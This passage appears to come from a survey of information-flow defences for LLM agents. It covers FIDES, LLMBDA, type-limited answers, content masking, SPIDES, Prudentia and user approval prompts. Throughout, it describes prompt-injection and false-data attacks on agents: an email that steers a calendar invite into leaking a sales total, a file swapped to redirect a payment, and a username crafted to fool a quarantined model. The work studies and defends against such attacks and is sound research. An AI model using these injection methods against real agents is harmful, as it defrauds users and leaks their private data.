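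The formal definition again compares four runs, with secrets and attacks in exchanged roles. Write *P*_a(*s*) for the run with secret *s* and attack *a*, and =_T when two runs have the same trusted results. For all secrets *s* and *t* and all attacks *a* and *b*,

*P*_a(*s*) =_T *P*_b(*s*) ⇒ *P*_a(*t*) =_T *P*_b(*t*).

If two attacks have the same effect on trusted data when the secret is *s*, they must also have the same effect when it is *t*. This rule prevents secrets from increasing an attacker's power over trusted data. As with robustness, the full definition leaves out uninformative cases, such as a choice between two equal secrets.

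Nonmalleable information flow combines robust declassification with transparent endorsement. The name comes from cryptography, where a malleable encryption scheme lets someone turn one encrypted message into a related one without reading it, much as Bob does with Alice's bid. Data that an attacker can change but not read must stay both secret and untrusted, and a program cannot get around this by endorsing the data before declassifying it.

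The combined definition has to let an endorsed value affect a later release. For example, a stranger's guess, once endorsed, should affect what the login page reveals. Earlier definitions guaranteed robustness only for programs with no endorsements. Cecchetti and colleagues instead compare runs under two attacks, up to a given release, only if the attacks have had the same effect on trusted data so far. They proved that their programming language enforces this condition without banning releases or endorsements, and they implemented the rules as a library for Haskell.

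### Leaks through a program's progress

An attacker can also learn something from whether a program keeps going. Cecchetti (2025), in *Nonmalleable Progress Leakage*, gives the example of a phone app that shows nearby attractions on a map. The phone looks up the user's exact location and general region, then runs the app maker's code to build the map. That code may send the region to the app maker's server but not the exact location. The app might hang for several reasons:

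- **Poor signal.** The phone may fail to find the location, which reveals a little about where the user is.
- **A server fault.** The server may stop responding, which reveals nothing about the user.
- **Malicious code.** The app maker may write code that hangs only if the user is at a particular address. The server can then infer the address because the app goes silent.

Many security checks ignore hanging, so they would accept the malicious code. Stricter checks forbid any leak through progress and would reject the whole app because of the poor signal. Cecchetti's condition, nonmalleable progress leakage, allows such a leak only if an attacker cannot steer it. It also adds a counterpart to transparent endorsement that stops secrets from affecting an attacker's control over the program's progress. The app can then tolerate poor signal and server faults without allowing the deliberate hang.

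Earlier versions of the four-run test could not make this distinction because they considered only runs that finish. Cecchetti compares partial runs instead. In Cecchetti's language, the programmer or an algorithm marks each place where a program may reveal that it has finished a block of code. The algorithm adds as few marks as possible and finds a secure placement whenever one exists. Cecchetti verified all the theorems in Rocq, a proof assistant. The language is small, with numbers as its only values and no ordinary declassification or endorsement. Cecchetti expects these to be easy to add, although the proofs would become considerably longer.

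Cecchetti notes that such a leak grows easily if a system restarts by itself, which is also the danger in CaMeL's retry loop.

### What the trusted-action policy allows

Costa and colleagues observe that the trusted-action policy in FIDES, used without its confidentiality rule, is a form of robust declassification. If an agent under this policy sends private data to someone who could not otherwise see it, the planner must have chosen to do so in a trusted context. Costa and colleagues therefore assume the release is intentional.

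Suppose Alex asks the agent to read the emails from Priya and Marco, schedule a meeting with Marco, and include Priya's sales total in the invitation. Alex's organisation trusts both colleagues, so the context label stays T, but only Alex may read the combined contents. The confidentiality rule would block the invitation because Marco may not see the total. The trusted-action policy alone allows it, since Alex asked for it and no stranger could have influenced the choice. The version of robustness for people who distrust one another would be stricter, because Marco's email was in the context and the invitation would give him access to the total.

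Now suppose the agent also reads the stranger's email, and Alex has asked it to invite anyone who wants a meeting and to include the sales total. The planner's context becomes U, and the policy blocks the calendar call whatever the email contains. The release mechanism is robust because the stranger sees nothing in any of the four runs, but the agent cannot finish the task.

FIDES can get further with an endorsement. The quarantined model reports whether any email asks for a meeting, and the planner reads that yes-or-no answer. A policy that accepts such answers as trusted then allows the calendar call. The planner asks the quarantined model for the meeting details and passes them to the calendar tool without reading them. If the policy does not check where the guest's address came from, the stranger sees the following:

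| Secret | Stranger advertises shoes | Stranger asks for a meeting |
|---|---|---|
| Total is 4 million | Nothing | An invitation containing 4 million |
| Total is 5 million | Nothing | An invitation containing 5 million |

The release is no longer robust, because the stranger can now cause it by asking for a meeting. Qualified robustness still holds because the stranger's influence passes through an answer that the system endorsed. Turning the confidentiality rule back on would stop the invitation, but it would also stop Alex from deliberately sharing the total with Marco.

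The looser form of the trusted-action policy can fail robustness even without an endorsement. Suppose Alex asks the agent to post a summary of all three emails to a chat channel that outsiders can read. The planner chooses the channel and the tool in a trusted context, so that decision has enough integrity. The summary does not, because the stranger's email may cause the quarantined model to include the sales total. If the policy does not check the label on the message, only the confidentiality rule can stop the leak.

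The yes-or-no answer can also leak private information. Suppose the stranger writes, "If sales were above 4.5 million, I'd like to meet." A quarantined model that reads all three emails together can use Priya's preview to decide whether this is a meeting request. If the system endorses the answer and sends an invitation, the stranger learns that sales were above 4.5 million, even if the invitation contains no figures. Transparent endorsement would forbid the system from trusting this answer, because the stranger influenced it but had no right to read it. Handling each email in a separate conversation avoids the problem, because the answer about the stranger's email then depends only on text the stranger already knows.

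### Endorsing data without releasing secrets

LLMBDA, the agent programming language by Garby and colleagues, avoids that leak differently. Its labels have separate parts for integrity and secrecy, and endorsement changes only the integrity part. If a value has the label (*i*, *s*) and a program in a trusted, public context endorses it to integrity *i*′, its new label is

(*i*′, *s*).

An endorsed password therefore remains secret. A yes-or-no answer that depends on Priya's preview also remains secret, so a tool that checks secrecy would refuse to send the stranger an invitation based on that answer.

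Garby and colleagues prove in Lean that this separation holds for every program in the language. They call the result insulated noninterference. It concerns an observer *m* who can see a value or not according to its secrecy label alone, whatever its integrity. Write *x* ~_m *y* if two starting states look the same to this observer, and ⟦*x*⟧_m for the probabilities of the results that the observer can see. Then

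*x* ~_m *y* ⇒ ⟦*x*⟧_m ⌣ ⟦*y*⟧_m.

The symbol ⌣ means that the two sets of probabilities could become equal if more runs finished. As in the theorem for programs without endorsements, a secret can affect whether a run finishes but nothing else that the observer sees. This is true for any untrusted data an attacker supplies and any endorsements the program makes.

The theorem protects only the part of the label that a program cannot relax. The same proof would work for a language that allows declassification but not endorsement, where it would protect integrity. If a program could relax the whole label, the theorem would guarantee nothing. A system that needs both endorsement and declassification, such as one that schedules a stranger's meeting and shares figures with Marco, still needs rules like those of nonmalleable information flow.

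The theorem also doesn't show that an endorsement was wise. Both successful attacks on Garby and colleagues' agent, Randori, involved the same task, in which a user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The agent endorsed the details and paid the attacker. No secret leaked, so the theorem held, but the user lost money. Blocking the endorsement would have stopped the attack, but it would also have prevented the agent from paying a genuine bill.

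### Stopping one endorsement from leading to others

In LLMBDA, an endorsement cannot raise a value's integrity above that of the context where the endorsement runs. Suppose an attacker's text causes a model to write code that endorses an account number. If the text still has its untrusted label, the code runs in an untrusted context and its endorsement has no effect.

This protection fails if the program has already endorsed the attacker's text. For example, an agent might endorse the meeting details in a stranger's email and then give them to a model that writes the next part of the plan. The new code runs as trusted even though the stranger may have influenced it, so it could go on to endorse anything else the stranger wants.

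Garby and colleagues propose a restricted operation, robust endorsement, that prevents such chains. It adds a permanent mark to everything it endorses. In Python-like form, it works as follows:

```
def robust_endorse(value):
    assert not has_mark(value)
    return add_mark(endorse(value))
```

Anything the program computes from a marked value also carries the mark, and the program stops if it tries to endorse such a value again. The system rejects model-written code that contains the ordinary `endorse` command, so the code has to use the restricted version. Tools that require trusted data must accept marked values too, or the endorsement would be useless.

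Skipping the second endorsement instead of stopping the program would require an "if" that depends on the value's label. In LLMBDA, the result of that test would be untrusted, so even a permitted endorsement inside the "if" would have no effect. Garby and colleagues say that a version that skips would need a new command, which might break the secrecy theorem.

They have no theorem that states exactly what robust endorsement achieves. One difficulty is that an attacker's influence over whether an endorsement happens may not show in a program's result. Suppose an attacker controls `first` and `second`, and compare these two programs:

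```
# Program A
if endorse(first):
    result = endorse(second)
else:
    result = nothing

# Program B
result = endorse(second if first else nothing)
```

Both programs give the same result with the same label, so they are indistinguishable under a definition based only on results. But in program A, the attacker's value of `first` decides whether the program endorses `second`, while program B always makes one endorsement.

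Garby and colleagues expect the restriction to interfere little with the banking tasks they tested. Each endorsement in those tasks applies directly to a value extracted from a file, such as an account number, and none depends on an earlier endorsement. Robust endorsement would therefore allow all of them, even if an attacker put the account number in the file.

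## Letting through only a small answer

Robust endorsement restricts when a program may trust a value, but not how much the value can contain, so a whole email could pass through. Agent designers can also restrict the size of what gets through. A quarantined model, which reads untrusted text but cannot call tools, has to answer a question with yes or no, or with one item from a fixed list, and only that answer reaches the planner. An attacker who takes over the quarantined model can still choose the answer, but cannot turn it into an instruction to send a password somewhere.

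### Constrained decoding and labels with types

A language model writes one token at a time, choosing each from a fixed set. In constrained decoding, the program running the model removes every token that would break a required format before each choice. If the format allows only yes or no, the model can output nothing else, whatever the email contains.

Costa and colleagues build this into FIDES. The planner gives the quarantined model a question, the names of the hidden variables to read, and an output format. The program stores the answer in a new variable, and the planner has to call another tool, `inspect`, to read it.

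FIDES also records the format in the answer's label. Next to the usual security label stands a type, and the types form a lattice ordered by how much information they can carry:

bool ⊑ enum["a", "b", "c"] ⊑ string.

A bool is a yes or no, an enum is one item from a list, and a string is any text. When the agent combines two values, both parts of their labels join:

(ℓ₁, μ₁) ⊔ (ℓ₂, μ₂) = (ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂, μ₁ ⊔ μ₂),

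where ℓ is the security label and μ the type. A yes-or-no answer about a stranger's email gets the label (U, bool), while a summary of the same email gets (U, string). Both are untrusted, but a policy can let the planner act on the answer and not on the summary.

*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) describes a similar design. The quarantined model may pass on only whole numbers, decimal numbers, yes-or-no values and items from a list that the developer has checked. In the shopping agent, this model reduces each customer review to two whole numbers, one of which is a score from 0 to 10 for how strongly the review supports the product. An agent that fixes software bugs could receive a file name, a line number and the type of bug. The researchers argue that none of these types can contain an instruction. They also keep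 lists short, because a long list of numbers could encode text. One very large number could do the same, so a number's range matters as well as its type.

### How the bits add up

An answer with *n* possible values carries at most log₂ *n* bits. Here are some examples:

| Answer | Possible values | Bits |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 |
| One of three tasks | 3 | 1.58 |
| A score from 0 to 10 | 11 | 3.46 |
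| One of three tasks for each of 20 emails | 3²⁰ ≈ 3.5 billion | 31.7 |
| 20 emails ranked by importance | 20! ≈ 2.4 × 10¹⁸ | 61.1 |

Costa and colleagues suggest letting the quarantined model pick from a list of tasks, such as scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply or forwarding the email. That leaves an attacker three choices for one email, but the answers for 20 emails carry 20 × log₂ 3 ≈ 31.7 bits, which gives the agent about 3.5 billion possible courses of action.

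The type lattice does not record how many answers the planner has received. Joining a label with itself gives the same label, so the planner's context has the same type after 20 yes-or-no answers as after one. A policy that checks only the type would therefore accept all 20. Costa and colleagues say that a policy can accept a yes-or-no answer because untrusted data then has only one bit of influence, but this holds only for a single answer.

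To limit the total, a system must keep a running count, as Trident does. *Trident* gives the example of a planner that asks whether a message contains an invoice, which takes 1 bit to answer, and then which of three known vendors sent it, which takes 1.58 bits. Under a 10-bit limit, an agent could sort six emails into three classes, using 9.5 bits, but not a seventh. Trident also counts the information in the length of a list, the order of its items and the presence of an optional field, unless the required format fixes them or the system hides them. Order matters because a ranking can carry almost twice as much information as the sorting, even though it contains no text from the emails, as the last row of the table shows.

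If one quarantined model reads all 20 emails together, a single hostile email could determine all 20 answers. If the system instead starts a fresh conversation for each email, a stranger who sent one of them controls only one answer, and can choose among three possibilities rather than 3.5 billion.

### The calendar request

For Alex's calendar request, the planner would read a yes-or-no answer on whether the emails ask for a meeting, then pass the hidden event details to the calendar tool. The basic trusted-action policy would block that call because the planner has read an untrusted answer. Costa and colleagues propose a looser policy that allows it, reasoning that a yes or no alone is unlikely to lead to an injection.

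One bit determines whether the entry appears, but the event details are free text that the quarantined model took from the email. The planner never reads these details, so they cannot change its plan, but a stranger could still put a misleading link in the title or add 50 guests.

A stricter design could also limit the details to fixed choices. Suppose the meeting must fall within the next 30 days, start in one of 16 half-hour slots, and include one guest from Alex's 50 contacts. If the program writes the title itself, the stranger can choose among 30 × 16 × 50 = 24,000 entries, or about 14.5 bits. But the agent then couldn't invite anyone outside Alex's contacts, because small answers work only when somebody can list the possible answers in advance.

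### One bit can decide a payment

Capping the number of bits limits how many outcomes an attacker can choose from, but not how bad the worst one is. Suppose Alex tells the agent to pay a builder $8,000 if the builder's email says the work is finished. Alex supplies the amount and the account number, and the planner reads only a yes or no, but one false yes is enough for the agent to send the money. Sorting 20 emails into three folders allows about 3.5 billion outcomes, but Alex could easily undo any of them.

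A sensible policy would therefore depend on the action as well as the answer's type. It might let an agent add a calendar entry based on a yes from an untrusted email, but not make a large payment.

Costa and colleagues did not measure how such policies perform. They left constrained decoding out of their AgentDojo tests of FIDES because they found that most of the tasks did not need it, so evidence of how well an agent works with small answers has to come from other systems.

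### Untrusted Content Masking

Some of the best evidence concerns agents that use a web browser. They see whole pages, where a shop's own buttons may appear next to strangers' reviews. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) presents a system that hides the untrusted parts of a page before the agent sees it. The site's owner marks those parts in the page's code, and the browser replaces each one with a placeholder such as `merchant-name:3`.

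The agent can ask a quarantined model about any placeholder. The agent chooses the type of answer, which may be yes or no, a date, a number within a stated range, or one item from a list of at most ten. The quarantined model writes out its reasoning first, but the program passes on only the final answer, and only if it has the right type.

The agent may ask at most five questions about each placeholder. If each answer is chosen from a list of ten options, five answers allow 100,000 combinations, or 16.6 bits. Numeric answers can carry more information, because the agent sets their range. The agent's instructions also forbid it from extracting hidden text letter by letter, which would get around the ban on free text.

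Nikolić and colleagues built ten websites with ten tasks each. Half the tasks need only trusted parts of the page, such as sorting products by name. The other half need text that masking hides, such as finding out how much the user sent to Sarah on Tuesday. In both groups, Claude Sonnet 4.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4 completed about as many tasks with masking as without it. Masking raised the typical cost of a task by 5% to 84%, depending on the model and the group. About 15% of tasks became cheaper, which the researchers attribute to less clutter on the page.

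They also tried 41 kinds of task on GitLab, a real application for managing code. The agents still solved most of them, but declared four unsolvable. All four need free text, such as the names of a project's three largest contributors, and the agent cannot list names it doesn't know as options. When the researchers let the quarantined model return text that a user had approved, the agents did as well as undefended ones.

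To test security, the researchers planted instructions in GitLab issues, reports that users write about a project. The agent had to post one comment if the issue mentioned critical data loss and another if it did not, so it could not ignore the text. With Claude Sonnet 4, 17% of the attacks succeeded against an undefended agent, 8% against an agent with a warning in its prompt, and none against the masked agent, which also completed every task.

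The result depends on correct labels. When the researchers wrongly marked the issue text as trusted, 6% of attacks succeeded. They also had a model identify the untrusted parts of a page from its structure alone. It missed no kinds of untrusted element on Reddit, about 7% of them on Booking.com and 11% on GitLab.

### Injected instructions and injected data

An injected instruction tells the agent to do something the user didn't ask for. Injected data gives the agent a false fact to rely on while it does the user's task. Letting through only a small answer, such as yes or no, stops injected instructions because the answer is too short to contain one. It doesn't stop injected data, because the agent can't tell from the answer alone whether it's true.

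Nikolić and colleagues looked for such attacks on GitLab by having Claude Sonnet 4.6 play an attacker who controls every answer from the quarantined model. Most of the attacks it found only made the agent fail at its task, but two were more serious:

- **The wrong project.** The user asks the agent to invite Marko to a project called "dotfiles". The agent cannot read the project names, so it asks about each hidden name in turn and acts on the first yes. A false yes for the attacker's project sends the invitation there.
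- **The wrong person.** The user asks the agent to give `stefan01` access to a project. An attacker has registered the name `stefan_i_am_the_right_person`, which appears in the search results and persuades the quarantined model to answer yes.

Both attacks are hard because the attacker has to guess the task in advance and fit the manipulation into a name. The researchers suggest asking about all the candidates at once and treating more than one yes as a sign of tampering. For product reviews, they ask about each review separately, so one hostile review can change only its own score and an attacker needs many reviews to change the overall result.

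*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) describes another attack, in which the attacker imitates the marks that separate one piece of data from the next. The model mistakes the attacker's text for trusted data, even if the imitation is inexact. These attacks often succeeded against defences that stop injected instructions. A constrained answer would keep the fake marks away from the planner, but the quarantined model could still misread them and give a wrong answer.

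Jacob and colleagues do not try to defend against false data, because it does not change the agent's task. By their definition, the attack on the builder's payment would not count as prompt injection.

### SPIDES

In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) measured the difference between the two kinds of attack. Their system, SPIDES, also hides the untrusted parts of web pages, as well as private data, but treats small answers more strictly. Its quarantined model can return any text, which stays hidden in a variable. Once the agent reveals even a yes or no about a stranger's text, the context becomes untrusted, and SPIDES asks the user to approve the next consequential action.

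The researchers built MicroNet, a set of 28 linked websites with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. Fifteen of the tasks are data-dependent. Fifty of the attacks inject instructions, and the other six inject false data. The table compares results for SPIDES and Untrusted Content Masking (UCM), averaged over five repetitions. The last two columns show how often the false-data attacks succeeded.

| Model | UCM, data-independent tasks completed | UCM, data-dependent | SPIDES, data-independent | SPIDES, data-dependent | False data, no defence | False data, UCM |
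|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 57.1% | 96.0% | 81.5% | 98.7% | 80.0% | 60.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 33.7% | 68.0% | 69.8% | 97.3% | 76.7% | 63.3% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 36.1% | 84.0% | 58.0% | 92.0% | 53.3% | 50.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 45.4% | 93.3% | 60.0% | 94.7% | 40.0% | 43.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 41.5% | 96.0% | 77.1% | 96.0% | 50.0% | 56.7% |

No injected instruction succeeded against either system, even though the researchers assumed that any injected instruction would take full control of a planner that read it. False data never succeeded against SPIDES but succeeded against UCM in 43.3% to 63.3% of runs. With Claude Opus 5 and Claude Sonnet 5, UCM did no better against false data than no defence. Each of these percentages comes from only 30 runs, so the differences between models may be due to chance. UCM's overall attack success rate was only 4.6% to 6.8% because so few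 of the attacks used false data.

SPIDES's perfect score depends on the user rejecting every request that an attacker has influenced. In the tests without attacks, where the user approved everything, SPIDES asked for approval an average of 1.84 times per completed task. It leaves the decision to a person instead of relying on a small answer.

UCM did much worse on the data-independent tasks because its quarantined model cannot return text, even for the agent to pass along unread. Zverev and colleagues also tested UCM+, whose quarantined model returns hidden text but gives the planner no readable answers. UCM+ completed more of the data-independent tasks than UCM did. On the data-dependent tasks, its completion rate was about 15 percentage points lower than UCM's with each of the three Claude models and slightly higher with GPT-5.6 Terra. An agent probably needs both hidden text and small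 readable answers. The full FIDES design provides both, but the researchers did not test that combination.

The high scores on data-dependent tasks call for some caution, because all 15 tasks used what the researchers call the negative version of the data. This probably means that the condition in the request was false, so the agent had nothing to do. If so, the scores show that the agents could check a condition, but not whether they could act when it was true.

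UCM's agents also called the quarantined model an average of 8 to 34 times per task, depending on the model. Even if each call returned only a yes or no, 34 calls could carry 34 bits, enough to select among about 17 billion courses of action. The limit of five questions applies to each placeholder separately, so it does not cap this total.

### Endorsing only values from a fixed list

The exception for small values is one reason Garby and colleagues consider FIDES hard to audit. A yes-or-no value from an untrusted source that affected a tool call might be the answer to a question the developer meant to allow, or a leak the developer never considered. Both have the same type, and nothing in the run distinguishes them.

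In LLMBDA, a small value gets no special treatment until the program explicitly endorses it. Garby and colleagues give the example of an agent that sorts incoming emails and uses the category as the subject of its reply. The mail tool accepts only a trusted subject, but the category comes from a quarantined model that read the email. They propose an operation that endorses the category only if it is on a fixed list. In Python-like form, it looks like this:

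```
def bounded_endorse(value):
    allowed = ["invoice", "meeting", "general"]
    copy = endorse(value)
    if copy in allowed:
        return copy
    return value
```

The program endorses a copy of `value` before checking it against the list. If it tested `value` first, the condition would depend on untrusted data, and an endorsement inside that branch would have no effect. If the copy is on the list, the program releases it. Otherwise it returns the original value, which is still untrusted, so the mail tool refuses it. The list has to be part of the program, because an attacker who could add to it could get any text endorsed. As with robust endorsement, model-written code may use only the restricted operation.

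A reviewer can now find every place where the program makes an exception and see which values it allows. Each call lets through at most log₂ *n* bits for a list of *n* values, but the bits add up over repeated calls. Garby and colleagues have not yet proved a formal limit on the total.

Garby and colleagues also acknowledge that a fixed list does not suit the banking tasks they gave their agent, Randori, because nobody can put every legitimate account number on a short list. Randori endorsed those numbers with the ordinary command, so its results do not show how well a fixed list works. They say the justification for trusting such values has to come from the user, who authorizes the agent to trust a file by asking it to pay the bill inside.

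## Asking a person to approve the action or the data

Not every request names the data that the agent will have to trust, so many systems ask the user during the task.

An agent can ask the user to approve an action or to endorse a piece of data. An approval allows one tool call, such as a payment of $200 to a particular account. The data behind the call remains untrusted, so the next consequential action needs another approval. If the user instead endorses the data, such as an email, they agree to trust it, and the agent can then act on it without asking again.

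### Ten errands in one email

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an email listing ten tasks that each require a consequential action. If the agent reads the email without the user's endorsement, its context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve each of the ten actions. If the user endorses the email, the agent can do all ten tasks after asking one question.

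That works well if the email is harmless. Suppose an attacker has added an eleventh item telling the agent to send Priya's sales preview to an outside address. With approvals, the agent would ask Alex about this item separately, and Alex could refuse. After an endorsement it won't ask again, so Alex has to spot the item before agreeing, and the item may not be visible to Alex. *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack in which a hidden note in a résumé sways an agent that screens job applicants.

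Mistakenly endorsing data can also do more damage than mistakenly approving an action. If Alex wrongly approves one call, the agent does one harmful thing and the email remains untrusted, whereas wrongly endorsing the email lets the attacker's text influence everything the agent does afterwards. But eleven similar prompts in a row encourage Alex to click without reading, so the harmful call might get through either way. Kolluri and colleagues did not measure which approach is safer, because their experiments involved no human users.

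### How Prudentia chooses what to ask

Kolluri and colleagues built an agent called Prudentia on top of FIDES, the system that hides untrusted data in variables. Prudentia uses the same label checks but gives the planner information about them. The planner in FIDES doesn't have the policies, so it may open a hidden email early in a task, after which every payment needs approval.

In Prudentia, each tool's description states whether the tool requires a trusted context, and the planner tracks its own context label. Before opening hidden data, the planner must call a planning tool and write down why it needs to read the data, why the quarantined model cannot do the job, and which consequential actions it expects to take afterwards. Its instructions are to put off opening data as long as possible and to finish other consequential actions first.

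The planner then chooses between two options:

- **Ask for an endorsement.** The instructions recommend this if the planner expects to make more than one consequential call after reading. If the user agrees, the system opens only the endorsed items and the context stays trusted.
- **Read without an endorsement.** The instructions recommend this if the planner expects to make at most one such call. The context becomes untrusted for the rest of the conversation, and the user has to approve that call. The system also opens all the other hidden data, since keeping it hidden would no longer save any approvals.

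An agent can read data without asking the user to endorse it if no consequential action follows. In one run, the user wanted a summary of a day's appointments and a password reset link. The planner opened the appointments and an email from the service, then replied without asking the user anything. The search had also found a password email from an AOL address. If the agent had taken the link from that email, no prompt would have warned the user, because the policy does not cover replies.

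Before it reads the data, the planner has to choose whether to ask for approval of the action or of the data. If Alex asks it to do whatever the email says, the email could list one task or ten. A wrong guess may lead to extra prompts but cannot remove a required one, because ordinary code determines when the system must ask.

The planner is also instructed to open original data, never the quarantined model's answers about it. The user may therefore have to endorse a whole email when a yes or no would have been enough. This loses the protection of letting through only a small answer.

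### Counting interventions

Kolluri and colleagues argue that earlier studies measured the drawbacks of information-flow control unfairly. Those studies compared secure agents that got no help from a user with undefended agents that could take any action. Many products ask the user before every consequential action, so a defence that makes some of these prompts unnecessary has a benefit that those studies did not measure.

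They propose two metrics. Take *n* tasks, and let τᵢ be the agent's run on task *t*ᵢ, ⟦*t*ᵢ⟧ the set of runs that complete the task, and *v*(τᵢ) the number of times the run needs the user. The human-intervention load is the total over completed tasks:

load = Σ *v*(τᵢ), for all *i* with τᵢ ∈ ⟦*t*ᵢ⟧.

The completion rate with at most *k* interventions is

TCR@*k* = (1/*n*) · |{ *i* : τᵢ ∈ ⟦*t*ᵢ⟧ and *v*(τᵢ) ≤ *k* }|.

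TCR@0 is the share of tasks the agent completes without help. The ten-errand task counts towards TCR@1 if the user endorses the email, but only towards TCR@10 and above if the user approves each call.

These results are averages over five repetitions on AgentDojo, with no attack under way. The basic agent asks for approval of every consequential action, while the others ask only when a call fails the policy check.

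| Model | Agent | Load | Completed, no interventions | Completed, at most one | Completed, no limit |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| o3-mini | Basic | 48.2 | 24.3% | 54.4% | 62.5% |
| o3-mini | Basic with flow control | 32.4 | 35.5% | 58.8% | 62.5% |
| o3-mini | FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% | 60.8% | 64.3% |
| o3-mini | Prudentia | 16.4 | 59.1% | 66.1% | 69.8% |
| GPT-4o | FIDES | 7.8 | 50.3% | 54.6% | 56.3% |
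| GPT-4o | Prudentia | 23.8 | 42.5% | 58.4% | 61.4% |
| o4-mini | FIDES | 36.8 | 53.2% | 68.5% | 75.7% |
| o4-mini | Prudentia | 19.2 | 59.4% | 70.3% | 73.2% |
| GPT-5 | FIDES | 41.3 | 57.1% | 72.7% | 78.9% |
| GPT-5 | Prudentia | 7.3 | 72.7% | 79.5% | 80.0% |

With o3-mini, checking labels eliminated about a third of the basic agent's approval prompts without reducing the number of tasks completed. Hiding untrusted data, as FIDES does, eliminated many more. Prudentia needed only slightly fewer approval prompts than FIDES, but it completed 9 percentage points more tasks without human help.

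Prudentia's advantage depends on how well the model plans. With GPT-4o, the oldest of the four models, Prudentia needed three times as many interventions as FIDES and completed fewer tasks alone. With GPT-5, it needed fewer than a fifth as many interventions as FIDES and completed 72.7% of tasks alone. The extra planning also adds to the bill. With GPT-4o, a task cost about twice as much in Prudentia as in FIDES, though no more than about six cents on average.

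The load leaves out failed tasks, so an agent that fails more often may appear to need less help. Kolluri and colleagues excluded these tasks because the agents mostly repeated actions that had already failed the check, and a real user would have stopped the agents. Both metrics also count an endorsement the same as an approval, although one endorsement can permit ten actions. An agent could therefore score well by asking for very broad permission.

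The results also depend on the assumption that people decide correctly. Kolluri and colleagues assumed that the user would approve every request in a completed task and stop any harmful action during an attack. The Trident paper instead tested FIDES with every request approved automatically, and some attacks got past it.

### WASP

Kolluri and colleagues also tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark for web-browsing agents. On its simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, attackers plant instructions in posts and in reports about code. The user's task is always to comment on a post or upvote it. The researchers counted an attack as successful if it diverted the agent from this task, even if the attacker didn't achieve their final goal.

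Across four models, 14.6% to 29.2% of attacks on GitLab and 36.1% to 61.1% on Reddit succeeded against the basic agent. None succeeded against Prudentia, which also needed no interventions. The basic agent needed an average of 1.0 to 3.7 per task, because clicking and typing both counted as consequential. Prudentia completed more tasks than the basic agent in seven of the eight combinations of model and website, and the same number in the eighth. The researchers attribute the difference to injected text confusing the basic agent.

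The WASP tasks are easy for a system that hides untrusted text because they are all data-independent. For example, an agent can find the upvote button without reading the post, so it never has to ask a person to endorse it. Prudentia's results on WASP show that it avoids unnecessary questions, but they don't show how well people answer necessary ones.

### Endorsement can also release secrets

Prudentia lets the user endorse data but not declassify it. Kolluri and colleagues left out declassification because whether a release is appropriate depends heavily on the situation. They prefer to ask the user about each call. For example, Alex may be happy to send the sales total only to Marco, and only after the company has announced it. An approval can cover one message to one recipient, whereas declassifying the total would let the agent include it in any message to anyone.

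An endorsement in Prudentia can still lead to a release. Its policy lets a tool send data out if either the planner chose the call in a trusted context or all the recipients may already read the data. After Alex endorses the email with the errands, the context counts as trusted, so the agent can follow the injected item and send Priya's preview to an outsider without another prompt, even though Alex was asked only about the email.

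Always checking the recipients would stop this release, at the cost of more prompts.

### How carefully people read prompts

Users of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, accept 93% of its permission prompts according to the company's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, and 97% according to its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most of the commands are probably safe, so these rates alone don't prove that users are careless. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code proposes, but that may be because they prefer another approach, not because they noticed a danger.

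A controlled test gives better evidence. Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks and replaced one permission prompt in each session with one for a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Fatigue made people less careful, but most testers missed the danger even when they had seen few prompts. Reducing the number of prompts, as Prudentia does, would therefore probably have only a limited benefit.

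The testers weren't working on their own projects, where they might have been more careful. Anthropic published the results to support its decision to have a model review Claude Code's actions by default, so it had an interest in showing that human review works badly.

Other studies found that people did better, though still not well:

- Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 34 people without a software background review all 18 actions of an agent in a simulated day. They refused 59.6% of the actions that went beyond the user's request and approved 94.1% of the necessary ones.
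- Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested several kinds of prompt. With a conventional one, people refused 45% of unsafe requests.

Unsuitable requests made up 7 of the 18 actions in the first study and half of all requests in the second. People may be more suspicious when they see a bad request every few minutes. Real attacks are much rarer, so Anthropic's result may be closer to everyday use, although its prompts also showed technical commands rather than plain descriptions.

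Anthropic found that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks turned off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), a study of how agents handle files, examined 290 reports of problems and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of the reports, the user had allowed actions automatically, sometimes to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approvals may come from habit, tiredness or pressure to finish work. A system that learned its rules from such approvals could wrongly treat them as considered consent.

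### What a prompt should show

Some prompts don't give even a careful user enough information to decide. In *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, 31 of the reports involved prompts that showed a command but not its effect on the user's files. For example, approving a routine-looking command like `python3 setup.py` lets the agent run whatever code the file contains.

An attacker may also influence the wording of an approval prompt. Kolluri and colleagues warn about this but leave the design of prompts to future work. Any field that a stranger can fill in may carry a message to the user. The GitLab username `stefan_i_am_the_right_person`, which misled a quarantined model in an earlier example, would look just as reassuring there. An agent's explanation of its request is no safer if the agent wrote it after reading the attacker's text.

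Code can write the important parts of the prompt from labels instead. In Microsoft's example policy for chat messages, a tool call has three possible outcomes, which are to allow it, deny it or ask the user. If the context is untrusted, the policy computes

missing = *M* \ *R*,

where *M* is the set of people in the chat channel and *R* the set of people permitted to read the message. If nobody is missing, the agent may send it. Otherwise, the system lists the people who would gain access and asks the user. An attacker cannot reword that list. The example shows account numbers, however, and Alex would need to see Marco's name.

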